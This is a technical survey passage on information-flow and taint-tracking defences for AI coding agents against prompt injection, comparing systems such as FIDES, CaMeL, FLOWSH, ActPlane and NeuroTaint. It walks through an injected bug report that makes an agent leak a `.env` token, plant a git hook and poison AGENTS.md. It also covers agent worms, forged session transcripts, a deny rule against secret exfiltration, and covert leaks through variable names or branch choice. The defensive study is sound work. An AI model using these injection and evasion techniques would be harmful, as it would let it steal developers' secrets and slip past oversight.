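The zero depends on labels that covered every attack in the test by construction. AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so the researchers marked a data field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. In a real project, somebody has to decide, without a list of future attacks, which fields a stranger could control.

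### Keeping text away from the model

This problem is partly avoidable, because the model doesn't need to see all the text it handles. FIDES can hide text behind variables. When a tool returns data, the system compares each field's label with the context label. If a field is more restricted, the system stores it in memory and shows the model only a name, such as `#read_emails_0`, so the context label doesn't change. If the model later uses that name as an argument, the system replaces it with the stored text and its label.

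Suppose a user asks an agent to send their three latest emails to a colleague on Slack. A plain agent reads the emails, so its next call comes from an untrusted context. An agent that keeps the emails in a variable can fetch and send them without seeing their contents. The choice of tool and the recipient are then trusted, and only the message is untrusted. A policy can require a trusted recipient and accept an untrusted message.

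If the user wants a summary, some model has to read the emails. FIDES uses a quarantined model, which is a separate model call without tools. It reads the hidden text and puts its answer into a new variable, labeled with the join of the context label and the text's labels. Simon Willison proposed this separation in 2023 as the Dual LLM pattern. An email can still cause the quarantined model to write an empty or misleading summary, but it cannot make the main agent call another tool.

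CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues, does all the planning at the start. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes it, a privileged model receives only the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python, which an interpreter runs. When the plan needs something from an untrusted document, such as an address, a quarantined model extracts it and the interpreter stores it as a variable. Each variable carries tags that record where the value came from and who may read it. Before every tool call, a policy allows or denies the call based on the tool, the arguments and their tags.

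The plan fixes the control flow, meaning which steps can happen and in what order. Isolation alone would not protect the data flow, because an attacker who cannot add a step may still change the address used in a planned one. The tags allow the policy to detect such changes. If a document supplies a new recipient for a confidential file, the tags show that the address came from the document and that the recipient does not have permission to read the file.

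*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo while completing a comparable share of tasks. CaMeL's use of Python weakens its guarantee somewhat. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that variables without fixed types, exceptions and code that inspects itself make a plan hard to analyze in advance. For instance, a value in an untrusted document can trigger an exception that changes which code runs next.

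Both designs work best when the agent's steps don't depend on what it finds. Costa and colleagues define a task as data independent if one sequence of tool calls and one final response would solve it whatever the data is. Forwarding three emails is data independent, but "If one of my emails asks for a meeting, put it in the calendar" is not, because the right calls depend on what the emails say.

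Fixing a reported crash is highly data dependent, because the choice of which file to open next depends on the error message, the code that produced it and whatever that code calls. Kim and colleagues rank agents by who decides the sequence of steps, from the developer in advance to the model as it works. Developers use coding agents largely because they don't already know the steps.

Still, hiding would prevent three of the four harmful artifacts in the bug-report example. The main agent could pass the hidden issue and one source file to the quarantined model, request a patch, and save the answer without reading it. The injection would never enter the main agent's context, so nothing would prompt it to touch `.env`, install a hook or write to AGENTS.md. The patch could still contain code that the attacker wanted, and it would keep its untrusted label until a maintainer read it.

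The first difficulty is choosing the source file. The quarantined model has no tools and can't search the project, and the main agent can't read the issue to find out where the crash happened. The main agent could ask the quarantined model to pick from a list of file names, but then the issue can influence what the agent does next. Test results are also a problem, because the tests run an untrusted patch, so their output is untrusted and the system hides it from the main agent. The main agent could send the output back to the quarantined model, ask for another patch, and repeat this until a yes-or-no answer indicated that the tests passed. That may be enough for a small bug in a known file, but it is much less promising for a fix that requires exploration. If the project's own source files also count as untrusted, as they do in GitHub's MCP server, the main agent can hardly read anything.

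AgentDojo offers some evidence on this, although only from office and web tasks. Data-dependent tasks make up 5% of its workspace tasks and 10% of its travel tasks, but more than 40% of those in the bank and Slack. With the checks on, GPT-4o completed the following shares:

| Environment | Plain agent, no checks | Plain agent, checks | FIDES with variables, checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
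| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Bank | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four environments, variables recovered about 8 of the percentage points lost to the checks. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, the gain was 16 points. Some of the remaining failures occurred because GPT-4o mixed up variable names and opened things it didn't need. With all checks off, using variables lowered GPT-4o's score by 23.7 points and o1's by only 6.3, so current models may well lose less.

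The other kind of failure comes from the policy itself, so better models won't remove it. Many of the bank tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, and FIDES blocked them because its policy forbids this. Coding agents routinely do the same with README files, build instructions and issues.

One of the successful tasks asked the agent to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. The agent judged a large amount suspicious and changed the password without opening the hidden description. This violated no policy because the benchmark labelled amounts as trusted. But anyone who sends a transfer chooses its amount, so in a real bank this decision would have depended on a value that a stranger can set.

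### Estimating which inputs mattered

If the model has already read everything, a system can still try to find out what it used. Siddiqui and colleagues propose a test for this. Suppose the model has answered a question from a set of documents, some of them untrusted. The system takes a more permissive label L′, removes every document that L′ doesn't cover, and measures how well the model can still predict its original answer. It accepts L′ if

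U(answer | all documents) − U(answer | documents that L′ covers) ≤ λ,

where U measures how likely the model finds the answer and λ is the loss that the operator will tolerate. The system searches for the most permissive labels that pass. If it finds one, it runs the model again on the smaller set of documents and returns the new answer with the new label.

The second run makes this safe even though the test is only an estimate and an attacker might fool it. The text that leaves the system comes from that run, which never received the removed documents, so a mistaken estimate makes the answer worse but leaves its label correct.

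Skipping the second run would be risky, even though the first answer is already there and the test indicates that the untrusted documents hardly affected it. In experiments with questions about pairs of news articles, one trusted and one not, the system sometimes chose a more permissive label than the correct one. Without a second run, each of these errors would have put a trusted label on an untrusted answer. They made up 23% of the system's label improvements with the 7-billion-parameter version of Llama 2 and 19% with the 70-billion version.

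Even with the second run, the method is slightly unsound. The new answer depends only on the permitted documents, but the decision to release it depends on all of them. Somebody who sees an answer with a public label can infer that the secret documents would not have changed the original answer much. This implicit flow is usually small. The method also assumes the input labels are correct, and an attacker can degrade it by adding distracting text until no permissive label passes the test.

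In 20 simple, hand-written conversations where an agent had retrieved a trusted and an untrusted source but needed only the trusted one, the system improved the label in 17 cases with the smaller model and 19 with the larger. Asking the model which source it had used worked in 9 and 16 cases, respectively. These results are for a model from 2023. Improvements were rarer on the news articles, at 57% of the cases where improvement was possible for the smaller model and 39% for the larger.

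In the bug-report example, the method could produce a patch that isn't secret. If the agent wrote the patch after opening `.env`, the conservative rule makes the patch secret. The system could remove from the conversation the token and everything the agent wrote after reading it, then have the model write the patch again. The new patch would be (untrusted, public), even if the agent had been trying to hide the token in the first one, because the model would not see the token during the second run. The patch would still be untrusted because fixing the crash requires the stranger's report.

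Running the model again takes time and money, so other researchers have tried to infer the flow from the first run. Sightline, a tool by Xu and colleagues, records how much weight each attention unit gives each input as the model produces its output. A simple classifier learns from labeled examples which attention patterns indicate that the model used an input. Xu and colleagues set the classifier's threshold to miss about 1% of real flows. On prompts from 2,103 groups of open-source projects, Sightline removed between 44% and 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model, and added 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call. The best competing method removed 22% to 38%. Xu and colleagues also report that when they used Sightline in an agent's information flow control, it removed about half of the unnecessary labels and no attack passed the integrity check.

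These figures amount to only a small reduction in labels overall. Only 12% to 14% of the inputs in these programs failed to reach the output, so removing about half of those labels leaves more than 90% of all labels in place. Typical program prompts are short and contain little that the model doesn't need, but a coding agent's long conversation may contain more unneeded text.

The 1% guarantee is also statistical. It holds on average, and only if new calls resemble the ones used to set the threshold, which gives an attacker a strong incentive to send calls that don't. The training labels come from three language models that judged whether the output *visibly* reflects an input. If an agent encoded the token in its variable names, those models would probably have labelled the token unused. Sightline is therefore a reasonable way to reduce label creep when the agent makes no effort to hide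 anything, but it isn't reliable when the agent might be hiding something.

*Crossing the NL/PL Divide* (Xu, Meng and colleagues, 2026), an earlier paper with the same lead author, studies the question from the programmer's side. Ordinary programs now send data to a model through an API and use its output, sometimes by running it as code. A static taint analysis, which examines a program without running it, loses track of the data at the model call. The paper covers 9,083 pairs of an input and a model output, taken from 4,154 Python files, and sorts the relationships between them into 24 types, such as verbatim copying, translation, a yes-or-no decision and the input being ignored. In about 15% of pairs, the input did not reach the output.

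They then took 62 files that contained a dangerous operation, such as running a string as code, and asked for 353 pairs whether an attacker who controlled the input could reach that operation through the model:

| Method | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Assume that every input reaches the operation | 31.2% | 100% |
| Drop inputs that the model didn't use | 34.6% | 98.2% |
| Ask a model (Claude Opus 4.6) to judge from the code, the prompt and the output | 75.9% | 80.0% |
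| Drop unused inputs, then ask the model whether the output reaches the operation | 98.0% | 87.3% |

Precision is the share of alarms that are correct, and recall is the share of real flows that the method finds. Marking all of the model's output as tainted produced 243 false alarms, and accounting for the inputs the model had ignored removed only 39 of them. Most of the false alarms arose because the program never passed the model's output to the dangerous operation, which ordinary code analysis can often establish. Much of the overtainting therefore happens outside the model, where exact rules for tracking taint exist.

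The best method still missed 14 of the 110 real flows. In 12 of these, the verifying model failed to follow the data through frameworks and callbacks. In the other two, the labeling model had wrongly marked an input as ignored, for instance a system prompt that subtly affected the style of the generated code. Only two flows were missed this way, but a careful attacker would look for this kind of influence.

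### Working it out from the logs

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool that analyzes the log of a finished session instead of labeling the model's output as it appears. It tries to establish which untrusted source influenced which sensitive action. It first builds a provenance graph, in which each tool call is a node and each edge records a possible path for the data. If the agent saved text to its memory store, NeuroTaint stores the labels with it and restores them when a later session retrieves the text.

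For each sensitive action, the tool then compares the arguments with every source that could have reached them. It moves from cheap tests to expensive ones:

1. It looks for a random marker that it attached to the source text when the agent first read it.
2. It looks for shared wording, and counts an overlap of 15% of the shorter text as a match.
3. It compares the meaning of the two texts with an embedding model, which turns each text into a list of numbers so that similar meanings lie close together.
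4. It splits a long source into pieces and compares each piece, because one malicious sentence barely affects the meaning of a whole web page.

If nothing matches, the source may still have caused the action without leaving any words in it. The tool therefore replaces the source with a neutral text, such as "No relevant information found", and asks a model whether the agent would still have made the same call. The tool counts a "no" as evidence of influence, but this answer is a prediction, and the confidence given with it is only the model's own estimate.

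Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, their own benchmark of 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. The untrusted content influences the action in only half of the scenarios. NeuroTaint scored an F1 (the harmonic mean of precision and recall) of 0.928, against 0.522 for FIDES.

The comparison isn't a fair test of FIDES. FIDES is an enforcement system, so it has to allow or block an action before it happens and must not miss a flow, whereas TaintBench measures which flows actually happened. Of the 106 false alarms counted against FIDES, 94 come from scenarios in which the agent read an untrusted source and then took an unrelated sensitive action. A conservative system has to treat these actions as tainted because it cannot verify that the model ignored the source. Blocking them burdens the user, but the guarantee against missed flows requires it, so these false alarms don't show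 that FIDES propagates labels incorrectly.

The missed flows are harder to explain. The benchmark's version of FIDES missed 92 of the 200 real flows, including 23 of the 40 in which a source changed the agent's choice of action without any of the source's text appearing in that action. The design that Costa and colleagues describe would easily catch these. A poisoned search result makes the context untrusted, every later call inherits that label, and a consequential call fails the check even if it contains none of the attacker's words. Cai and colleagues appear to have tested something narrower, which they describe as a method that treats a path from source to sink as strong evidence of a flow.

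On four of the 20 frameworks, their version raised no alarms in 80 scenarios, which looks more like an integration problem than a property of the method. Excluding those frameworks would raise that version's F1 to about 0.58. A detector that flagged every scenario would have scored 0.67, and a fully conservative system would score close to that.

The comparison is fairer on flows that cross sessions, where the benchmark's version of FIDES missed 25 of 30 and NeuroTaint missed two. Labels that exist only while a session runs can't track data into a later session. On two older benchmarks, which test only whether an action was unsafe, the two tools performed almost identically.

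NeuroTaint is better understood as an aid to investigation, because it can't stop the push that leaked the token. It adds about a quarter of a second per session and can show a maintainer which issue probably led to which change. That would help after an attack, or when someone has to decide which of many untrusted files to review first.

NeuroTaint would also face two problems with code that its overall score doesn't show. The first is that it wrongly flagged all 14 TaintBench scenarios in which an action merely concerns the same topic as an untrusted source, and a bug report and an honest patch for it always concern the same topic. The second is that an agent could disguise the token by encoding it in variable names, which would leave the tool neither the token's wording nor its meaning to match. Cai and colleagues exclude hidden messages of this kind from their threat model. The counterfactual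 question could expose the encoding in principle, since the agent would have chosen other names if it had never seen the token, but the judge would have to work that out from names that look ordinary.

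## Can a label stay with a file through shells, commits and later sessions?

When a tool writes a file, FIDES labels the file according to everything the tool may have read. Someone can list those inputs in advance for a tool that fetches an issue or sends an email, but not for a shell, which coding agents use for much of their work.

Suppose the agent in the bug-report example copies the token with a script instead of a visible command. It writes `setup.sh` and runs it, and the script opens `.env`, writes the test fixture and creates the pre-commit hook. The harness, the software that runs the agent's loop and its tools, handles only two calls, one to write `setup.sh` and one to run it. If it updates labels from tool calls alone, the fixture and the hook won't be labeled.

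*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin et al., 2026) describes an agent that uploads a status report to GitHub, copies a sensitive inventory over the report, and then repeats the upload. A monitor has to allow the first upload and refuse the second, but the two commands are identical, so inspecting their text more closely doesn't help.

The harness could instead label the output of every shell command untrusted and secret, and ask for approval each time. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) tested this approach on Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks, and found that it needed 9.4 approvals per completed task. The paper's own system, which labels each command by what it opened, completed the same number of tasks with 0.4 approvals each. Fewer requests are better because users pay less attention as prompts accumulate, according to Anthropic, which also reports that users approve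 about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts.

### Labels in the operating system

A monitor has to work at the level of the operating system to find out what a command opened, because every program goes through the operating system to reach a file or a network. The research systems Asbestos (2005), HiStar (2006) and Flume (2007) worked at this level. They put labels on processes as well as data, so a program that read a secret file became subject to the file's restrictions.

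Asbestos and HiStar needed a modified operating system. Flume ran on Linux, but it checked its policy when a program read something. Kim and colleagues point out that Flume would refuse to open a confidential file while a public network connection was open, even if the program never used the connection. These systems also did not account for language models. The kernel, the core of the operating system, can treat an agent's whole session as a single process, whatever the model read during it.

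Most of the 2026 systems for agents use eBPF, a Linux feature that lets an administrator load small, automatically checked programs into a running kernel. These programs run whenever a process performs a chosen operation, such as opening a file or starting another process. They work on an ordinary Linux system and cover scripts in any language the agent uses.

### Following the hook

The simplest of these systems is the monitor that Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-Warden*, describe. It keeps a one-bit marker on each process and file, which means that the agent, or something downstream of it, may have influenced that process or file. The marker spreads by four rules:

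- A marked process marks every process it starts.
- A marked process marks every file it writes.
- A process that reads a marked file becomes marked.
- A marked process that exits marks its parent.

The paper also writes the rules as one equation. A row of zeros and ones, τ, records what has a marker, and a matrix C records which process or file each event connects to which. After each event,

τ(t+1) = τ(t) ∨ (τ(t) ⊗ C(t)),

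where ⊗ carries markers along the connection and ∨ means "or". Because of the "or", no event ever removes a marker.

The marker belongs to the file's inode, which is the filesystem's record of a file independent of its name, so renaming a file doesn't clean it. The pre-commit hook would pass through the rules like this:

| Event | Rule | What becomes marked |
|---|---|---|
| Monitoring starts | The operator designates the agent | The agent |
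| The agent runs `setup.sh` | Process to child | The shell that runs the script |
| The script writes the hook | Process to file | The hook |
| Later, the developer runs `git commit` in a separate terminal | None applies | Nothing |
| Git starts the hook, and a new shell reads its text | File to reader | The new shell |
| The hook finishes | Exiting child to parent | Git |
| Git stores the commit | Process to file | The commit's files |
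| Git finishes | Exiting child to parent | The shell in the developer's terminal |

The hook connects the developer's commit to the agent, which a log of the agent's tool calls could not do because the agent didn't start that Git process. Cui and colleagues tested a similar chain, in which an agent's script wrote and renamed a file and an unrelated program read it. Agent-Warden recovered the whole chain in all 120 runs, 30 for each combination of two storage methods and two machines. It slowed their workloads by 0.2% to 3.5%.

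As the end of the table shows, once the terminal's shell has a marker, every command the developer types there inherits it, even commands unrelated to the agent. The exit rule is meant to keep short-lived helper processes connected to whatever started them, and Cui and colleagues accept that it creates some false connections. The marker is less informative than a FIDES label because it covers everything the agent writes, even before the agent has read an issue or a secret.

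Agent-Warden records but does not block, so a maintainer could discover that a hook written by the agent had run only after the fact. The markers also exist only in memory, so they disappear when the machine restarts or the kernel drops the file's record to free memory. If a developer shut the machine down overnight, the hook would be unmarked the next day. In the experiment, the unrelated program read the file only tens of seconds after the agent had finished.

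The rules as written also lack a step that passes a label from a program file to the process that runs it. A hook written as a shell script still marks the shell, because the shell has to read its text, but a compiled hook might not mark anything.

### Rules that the kernel enforces

Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *ActPlane*, use labels to stop operations as well as to record them. An ActPlane rule names a source, an operation, an effect and a reason that goes back to the agent. The effect can be `notify`, which only sends advice, `block`, which refuses the operation before it happens, or `kill`, which ends the process afterwards. A rule for the token would look roughly like this:

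```
source TOKEN = file "**/.env"
rule keep-token-local:
  block connect "*" if TOKEN
  because "This process holds data from .env."
```

Any process that reads `.env` gets the TOKEN label, passes it to its children and to the files it writes, and can no longer open a network connection. Rules can also depend on the order of events. One rule, taken from a real project, stops a commit unless the tests have passed since the source code last changed.

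Zheng and colleagues studied the instruction files for agents in 64 popular repositories to find out how often projects need this kind of memory. Of 2,116 statements, 1,361 told the agent to do or avoid something. A monitor could judge 29% of these from a single event, such as a push to the main branch. Another 16% needed a record of what had happened earlier or where data had come from. The rest depended on the contents of files (38%) or on matters such as whether the agent explained its reasoning (17%).

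One statement that needs state, "Data read from .env must not reach the network," is the rule above in plain English. At least one statement that needs state appeared in 81% of the repositories. Many of these are about the order of development work, though, so the study is stronger evidence that projects need a monitor that keeps state than that they need taint tracking in particular.

The researchers then compared ActPlane with checks on individual tool calls. They took 38 rules and generated five agent sessions for each, two that obeyed the rule and three that broke it. One session broke it in a direct tool call, one through a script, and one through a file that looked harmless. A language model judged the outcomes:

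| System | Violations corrected, of 114 | Obedient sessions left alone, of 76 |
|---|---|---|
| Language model that reviews each tool call | 44 | 48 |
| Pattern matching on tool calls | 38 | 48 |
| FIDES | 41 | 52 |
| ActPlane without reasons | 27 | 75 |
| ActPlane | 86 | 58 |

The tool-level systems caught almost none of the violations hidden in harmless-looking files. A violation counted as corrected only if the agent changed course after the system intervened. When ActPlane gave no reasons for intervening, it scored low because the agent often didn't work out what it had done wrong. It still detected 75.4% of violations, close to the full system's 77.2%. A hijacked agent can't be expected to correct itself, so detection rates matter more for taint tracking. The tool-level systems detected 34% to 40% of violations.

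The results of this test depended mostly on the rules, which a language model translated from English. Some were too narrow, and the detection rate rose to 94.7% after one round of revision. Nobody in the test was trying to evade ActPlane itself, so these figures apply better to careless agents than to hostile ones.

ActPlane slowed replayed agent sessions by 1.9% with 32 rules, and its overhead stayed below 8.4% with 100 rules, even when compiling the Linux kernel. When labels build up until they block ordinary work, Zheng and colleagues recommend starting a fresh subprocess, which clears inherited labels. They also say that an agent cannot remove safety labels set by a higher authority. A fresh subprocess therefore has to keep those labels, or a hijacked agent could remove them by starting another process.

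### A connection that is already open

The sample rule for the token can't stop a leak through a Git push, because the rule applies only to new connections. Git connects to the server before working out which files to send, so the connection is already open when Git reads the fixture.

In *ContractWarden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026), a human assigns each sensitive file one of three settings before a task starts: `allow`, `deny` or `no_egress`. A program may read a `no_egress` file but then loses network access, as does any program that receives data from that program. The restriction follows data through intermediate files, pipes and local sockets. The kernel checks it when a program creates a connection and again whenever the program sends data.

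ContractWarden passed all 570 runs of 19 tests. In one test, a program opened a connection and sent data successfully, then read a restricted file, and its next send failed. In another, one task copied restricted data into an ordinary file, and a second task lost its network access after reading the copy. The researchers themselves chose the 19 properties to test, and they used scripted programs rather than agents working on real tasks.

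ContractWarden doesn't let an exiting child process restrict its parent, so the developer's terminal would stay usable after the hook ran. But restrictions do pass through pipes, and a harness usually receives a command's output through one. If the command has read `.env`, the harness would be restricted too. Most coding agents call their model over the network, and ContractWarden has no list of exempt destinations, so under its rules the agent could no longer call its model.

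The overhead was 12–13% in a virtual machine and 36–62% on a physical one. ActPlane's overhead on the same tests was higher, at up to 179%. These figures are far above the 1.9% that ActPlane adds to an agent session because the tests do little besides open and read files, while an agent session often pauses to wait for the model.

### Holding changes until the command ends

FLOWSH checks a command's effects before they reach the project. It runs each command in a sandbox, records which files the command and its subprocesses open and which servers they contact, and computes one label for the whole command:

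label(command) = label(agent's context) ⊔ labels of the files opened ⊔ labels of the servers contacted

If the agent passes hidden variables to the command, the command's label also includes theirs. A temporary layer holds file changes until the command finishes. A network request can't be undone once a server has received it, so a proxy checks each one before it leaves.

The sample policy lets untrusted commands write ordinary project files but not `.git/hooks`. When the agent runs `setup.sh` after reading the issue, FLOWSH holds the hook and prompts the developer. The developer has to accept or reject all of the script's changes together, because applying only some of them could break the project. Rejecting the hook therefore also discards the fixture.

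Kim and colleagues tested almost exactly this attack. In two of their task types, an agent implements a feature or fixes a GitHub issue while an injection tries to overwrite the pre-commit hook. They assumed that the attacker controlled everything the model wrote once the injected text reached it, so their results don't depend on how well the model resists injections. With nobody available to give approval, FLOWSH blocked all 40 attack runs in which the injected text reached the model, while a sandbox without restrictions stopped none of 51. This is strong evidence that FLOWSH protects the files and secrets covered by those tests.

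Under FLOWSH, the agent completed 58.8% of office and software tasks without approvals, compared with 94.1% in the unrestricted sandbox. With an ideal approver, who allowed every harmless request and refused every attack, it completed 88.2%. Completed tasks took 17% to 34% longer. FLOWSH also ends all of a command's processes when the command ends, so an agent cannot leave a development server running between commands.

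Tether also runs commands in a temporary layer, but it tracks data in finer detail. If the agent copies `.env` with a separate `cp` command, Tether labels the copy secret and doesn't change the label on the agent's context. A hook the agent writes afterwards is therefore not labeled secret, which avoids the overtainting that FIDES produced in the earlier version of this example. If one script both copies the file and writes the hook, Tether has to assume the token may have reached the hook.

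On two benchmarks for coding agents, Tether blocked every attack within its scope and wrongly stopped 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless sessions. Sistla and colleagues excluded attacks that broke no rule about data flow or that went through databases, background services and other things Tether doesn't trace. Tether can block all contact with an untraced service, but it cannot follow data through one.

### Where each system keeps its labels

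The systems differ considerably in how long their labels last:

| System | Where it keeps a file's label | After a restart | Can it block? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-Warden | In memory, with the inode | Gone | No |
| ActPlane | In kernel tables | No way of restoring it described | Yes |
| ContractWarden | In memory, with the inode | Gone, apart from files a human has listed | Yes |
| Tether | In the monitor's own table, by path | No way of restoring it described | Yes |
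| FLOWSH | On disk, with the inode | Still there | Yes |

FLOWSH stores its labels in extended attributes, small named fields that the filesystem keeps with a file. Commands inside the sandbox can't change them. Tether's table still tracks a file after a command renames it, and Tether clears the entry when a command deletes the file.

### When the next session opens the file

Even a label on disk helps only if the next session checks it. In *AgentLoupe*, Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026) built a monitor that traces actions back to a particular exchange with the model. It intercepts the agent's messages to the model before they are encrypted, gives each new prompt its own label in the kernel, and passes that label to the processes, files and network connections that result from the prompt.

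In a test with Claude Code, one session wrote an instruction into AGENTS.md that told agents to run a command whenever they received an ordinary question. A later session loaded the file and ran the command. The tracking tool AgentLoupe connected the two sessions because AGENTS.md still carried the label of the exchange that had written it. AgentLoupe's overhead was at most 8%. Bao and colleagues report only two such cases and haven't measured how often the tool misses a connection or reports a false one.

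AgentLoupe starts a new label whenever the user sends a prompt and records a link to the previous one. This keeps the record readable for investigators, and it is safe because AgentLoupe only observes. A system that blocked actions would have to follow the links or join the labels. Otherwise, after the developer's next harmless prompt, it would no longer connect the agent's actions to the poisoned file the agent had just loaded.

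Tainted text can return to the model's context through session transcripts as well as AGENTS.md. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) reports that deleting a memory file doesn't remove the notes in it, because the session transcript contains a copy. When the researchers forged a record in the transcript's format and resumed the session, all three command-line agents they examined loaded it as a message from the user, in eight out of eight runs each. Transcripts therefore need labels too, and the harness has to check those labels before it resumes a session.

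Zha and Wang (2026), in *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms*, put the check at the moment of reloading. Like the simplest version of FIDES, their system taints every file that a model writes after reading untrusted text, until something outside the model clears the label. An attack then has to complete much the same three steps that Xie and colleagues measured,

tainted write → exposed read → high-risk action,

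where an exposed read puts the file's contents back into a model's context. Their defense refuses the exposed read if the agent can still take high-risk actions, such as running shell commands or sending messages. If the untrusted text arrives from outside, with no earlier write to catch, the system allows the read and restricts those actions afterwards.

The researchers found 31 places in three open-source agent frameworks where an agent could save text that would later return to a model's context. A test worm used them to spread across three agents, including agents on different frameworks, with no human action after the first message. The researchers applied the defense to one framework, and it stopped every attack they had demonstrated there. They don't report how many runs they did or how often the defense wrongly blocked work, so it is hard to know how much it would disrupt legitimate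 use.

Zha and Wang also prove that no attack can complete the three steps if labels persist across sessions and stay with the file itself instead of its path, and if the system controls every exposed read and high-risk action. Of the systems in the table, FLOWSH comes closest to supplying such labels.

The rule is awkward for source code. An agent that has read a stranger's issue taints every file it edits, so it can't reread its own patch while it still has a shell. A compiler or test runner may process the tainted file if it returns only a restricted result, such as an error code, but debugging usually requires the full error message. The approach suits standing instructions and memory better. The researchers propose locking fixed instruction files while the agent runs and allowing only short, structured entries into trusted memory.

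### Saving and archiving

All these systems can lose a label when a file passes through something they don't control, such as a text editor. Many editors save by writing a new file and renaming it over the old one. The new file has a new inode, so a label attached to the old inode is lost.

Agent-Warden can keep the label when an editor saves a file as a new one, provided it tracks the editor reading the old file and writing the new one. FLOWSH tracks only the commands in its sandbox, so a file that the developer saves in a normal editor may lose its label. In FLOWSH's sample configuration, unlabeled files count as untrusted and readable only by the user, so losing the label makes the file more restricted. If a team chose a looser default to avoid interruptions, any save that dropped the label would make a tainted file count as clean. To preserve the exact label, either the editor has to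 copy the extended attributes or the monitor has to track the editor.

Archives can also lose the labels of many files at once. Some formats can hold extended attributes, but common tools leave them out unless the user asks. If a monitored command unpacks the archive on the same machine, every file inside inherits the archive's label. On another machine, even that label is missing. To carry the labels across, the archive would need a list of its files and their labels, signed by something the recipient trusts. Otherwise, whoever packs the archive could label its contents as trusted.

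### Commits

A Git commit records each file's name, contents and mode, which distinguishes, for example, an executable file from a symbolic link. It also records the parent commits, the author and committer, their dates and a message. It doesn't record extended attributes.

On the developer's own machine, a label can still survive the commit. Git stores committed contents in ordinary files under `.git`, and a monitored Git process would label those files as it wrote them. A later push reads those files, so the check on the token still works. But Git periodically packs many stored objects into one file, and FLOWSH gives each file a single label, so one secret fixture could cause the project's whole packed history to be labeled secret.

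A colleague who clones the repository gets none of the labels. FLOWSH labels downloaded data by server, so everything from GitHub gets the same label, whether a maintainer or a stranger wrote it.

The commit message could carry a label, and some coding agents already add a line to it naming themselves as co-author. *Agents on the Patch Path* (2026) uses these lines, along with the names of known bot accounts, to find security fixes that involved AI. These traces are visible only if they survive the project's merge process, and the study doesn't verify the accounts behind the names. More importantly, they show that an agent took part but not what it had read. A hijacked agent that writes its own commit message could also omit the co-author line.

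A trusted component outside the agent would have to record each file's label. It could store the label under the hash Git computes from the file's contents, so the record would survive renames and reorganized commits. Any edit changes the hash, so each new version would need a new record that takes the old label into account. Signed provenance records, which some build systems already produce, would be a good place to store this information.

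### Build servers and package registries

A remote build server usually starts from a clean machine and downloads the project, so it has no local labels. It would have to fetch the label records for the commit, treat a missing record as untrusted, and pass the combined label on to whatever it builds. A build cache, such as the one in the Cline case, would have to keep a label with each entry.

Package registries can make a label misleading. FLOWSH's sample configuration treats data from package registries as trusted and data from other servers as untrusted, but it also lets an untrusted session send public data to any server. An agent with permission to publish could therefore upload a package built from tainted code, and the next agent to install it would receive files labeled as trusted, even though nobody had decided to endorse them.

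The registry could prevent this by returning a label with each version of each package, or the client could keep its own list of reviewed versions. Kim and colleagues suggest accepting finer labels from trusted remote hosts as a future extension. If the registry supplied the labels, the recipient would depend on the registry's information about how each package was made.

### Tainted build tools

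A build's output also depends on the tools that produced it. In his 1984 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Unix co-creator Ken Thompson described a compiler that inserted a back door whenever it compiled the system's login program. Whenever it compiled a new version of itself, it also inserted the malicious code into the new compiler. Thompson could then delete that code from the compiler's source, and every later compiler built with the tainted one would still contain it. Nobody could find it by reading the source of the compiler or the login program.

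A label computed from source files alone would call the resulting login program trusted. The tools have to count as inputs:

label(output) = label(source) ⊔ label(compiler) ⊔ labels of everything else the build reads or runs

FLOWSH and AgentLoupe can apply this rule locally because they treat running a labeled file as receiving data from it. On a build server, the image containing the compiler would need its own label, with a record of which earlier compiler built it.

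A coding agent can create this situation by editing a build script or a code generator as part of an ordinary task. The join then taints everything that the project builds with the edited file. If the agent has tainted a compiler that later compiles itself, restoring the original source isn't enough to remove the label. Somebody also has to rebuild the compiler with a tool that the agent's changes never reached.

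## How much can a compromised agent leak despite the labels?

A hijacked agent can leak a secret through its choices even if every label survives shells, commits and build servers. In the bug-report example, each copy of the token would carry a secret label, and a monitor would stop any file with that label before it reached the public repository. The agent could still reveal the token through choices such as which branch it pushes or the order in which it lists a file's imports. How much it can leak depends on how many choices an outsider can see and how many options each one offers.

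### Noninterference and explicit secrecy

Noninterference is the strongest guarantee a labeling system can give about a secret. It means that changing the secret changes nothing an outsider can see. Let d₁ and d₂ be the contents of two machines, and let d₁ ≈ d₂ mean that their public data is the same, whatever their secrets are. Let run(d) be the contents of a machine after the agent has finished working on it. Noninterference requires that

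if d₁ ≈ d₂, then run(d₁) ≈ run(d₂).

To test whether an agent can leak secrets despite the labels, someone could put different secret tokens on two otherwise identical machines, run the agent on both and look for any difference in their public output, which would be a leak.

FIDES guarantees a weaker property, explicit secrecy. Let g be the combined effect of the tool calls that the agent made on the first machine, as a function that also applies to other machines. Explicit secrecy requires that

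if d₁ ≈ d₂, then g(d₁) ≈ g(d₂).

This test runs the agent only once and replays its tool calls on the second machine. If one call copied `.env` into the public repository, the replay publishes a different token and the comparison exposes the leak. But suppose the agent pushed branch A because the token's first bit was 0, and would have pushed branch B if it had been 1. Both machines push A, so the comparison finds no difference, even though anyone who sees which branch arrived can learn that bit.

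The replay also repeats any text the model typed into a call, so a token pasted into a message would pass this test. FIDES's labels are stricter than the formal property in this case, because the context label marks the message as secret.

The labels don't stop an agent from leaking information through its choices, though. In FIDES, text stored in a variable keeps its own label no matter which model response selects it. An agent could hold two public comments in variables, learn one bit of the token, and post the comment that matches that bit. The sample confidentiality rule checks the comment's label, which is public, so it allows the post.

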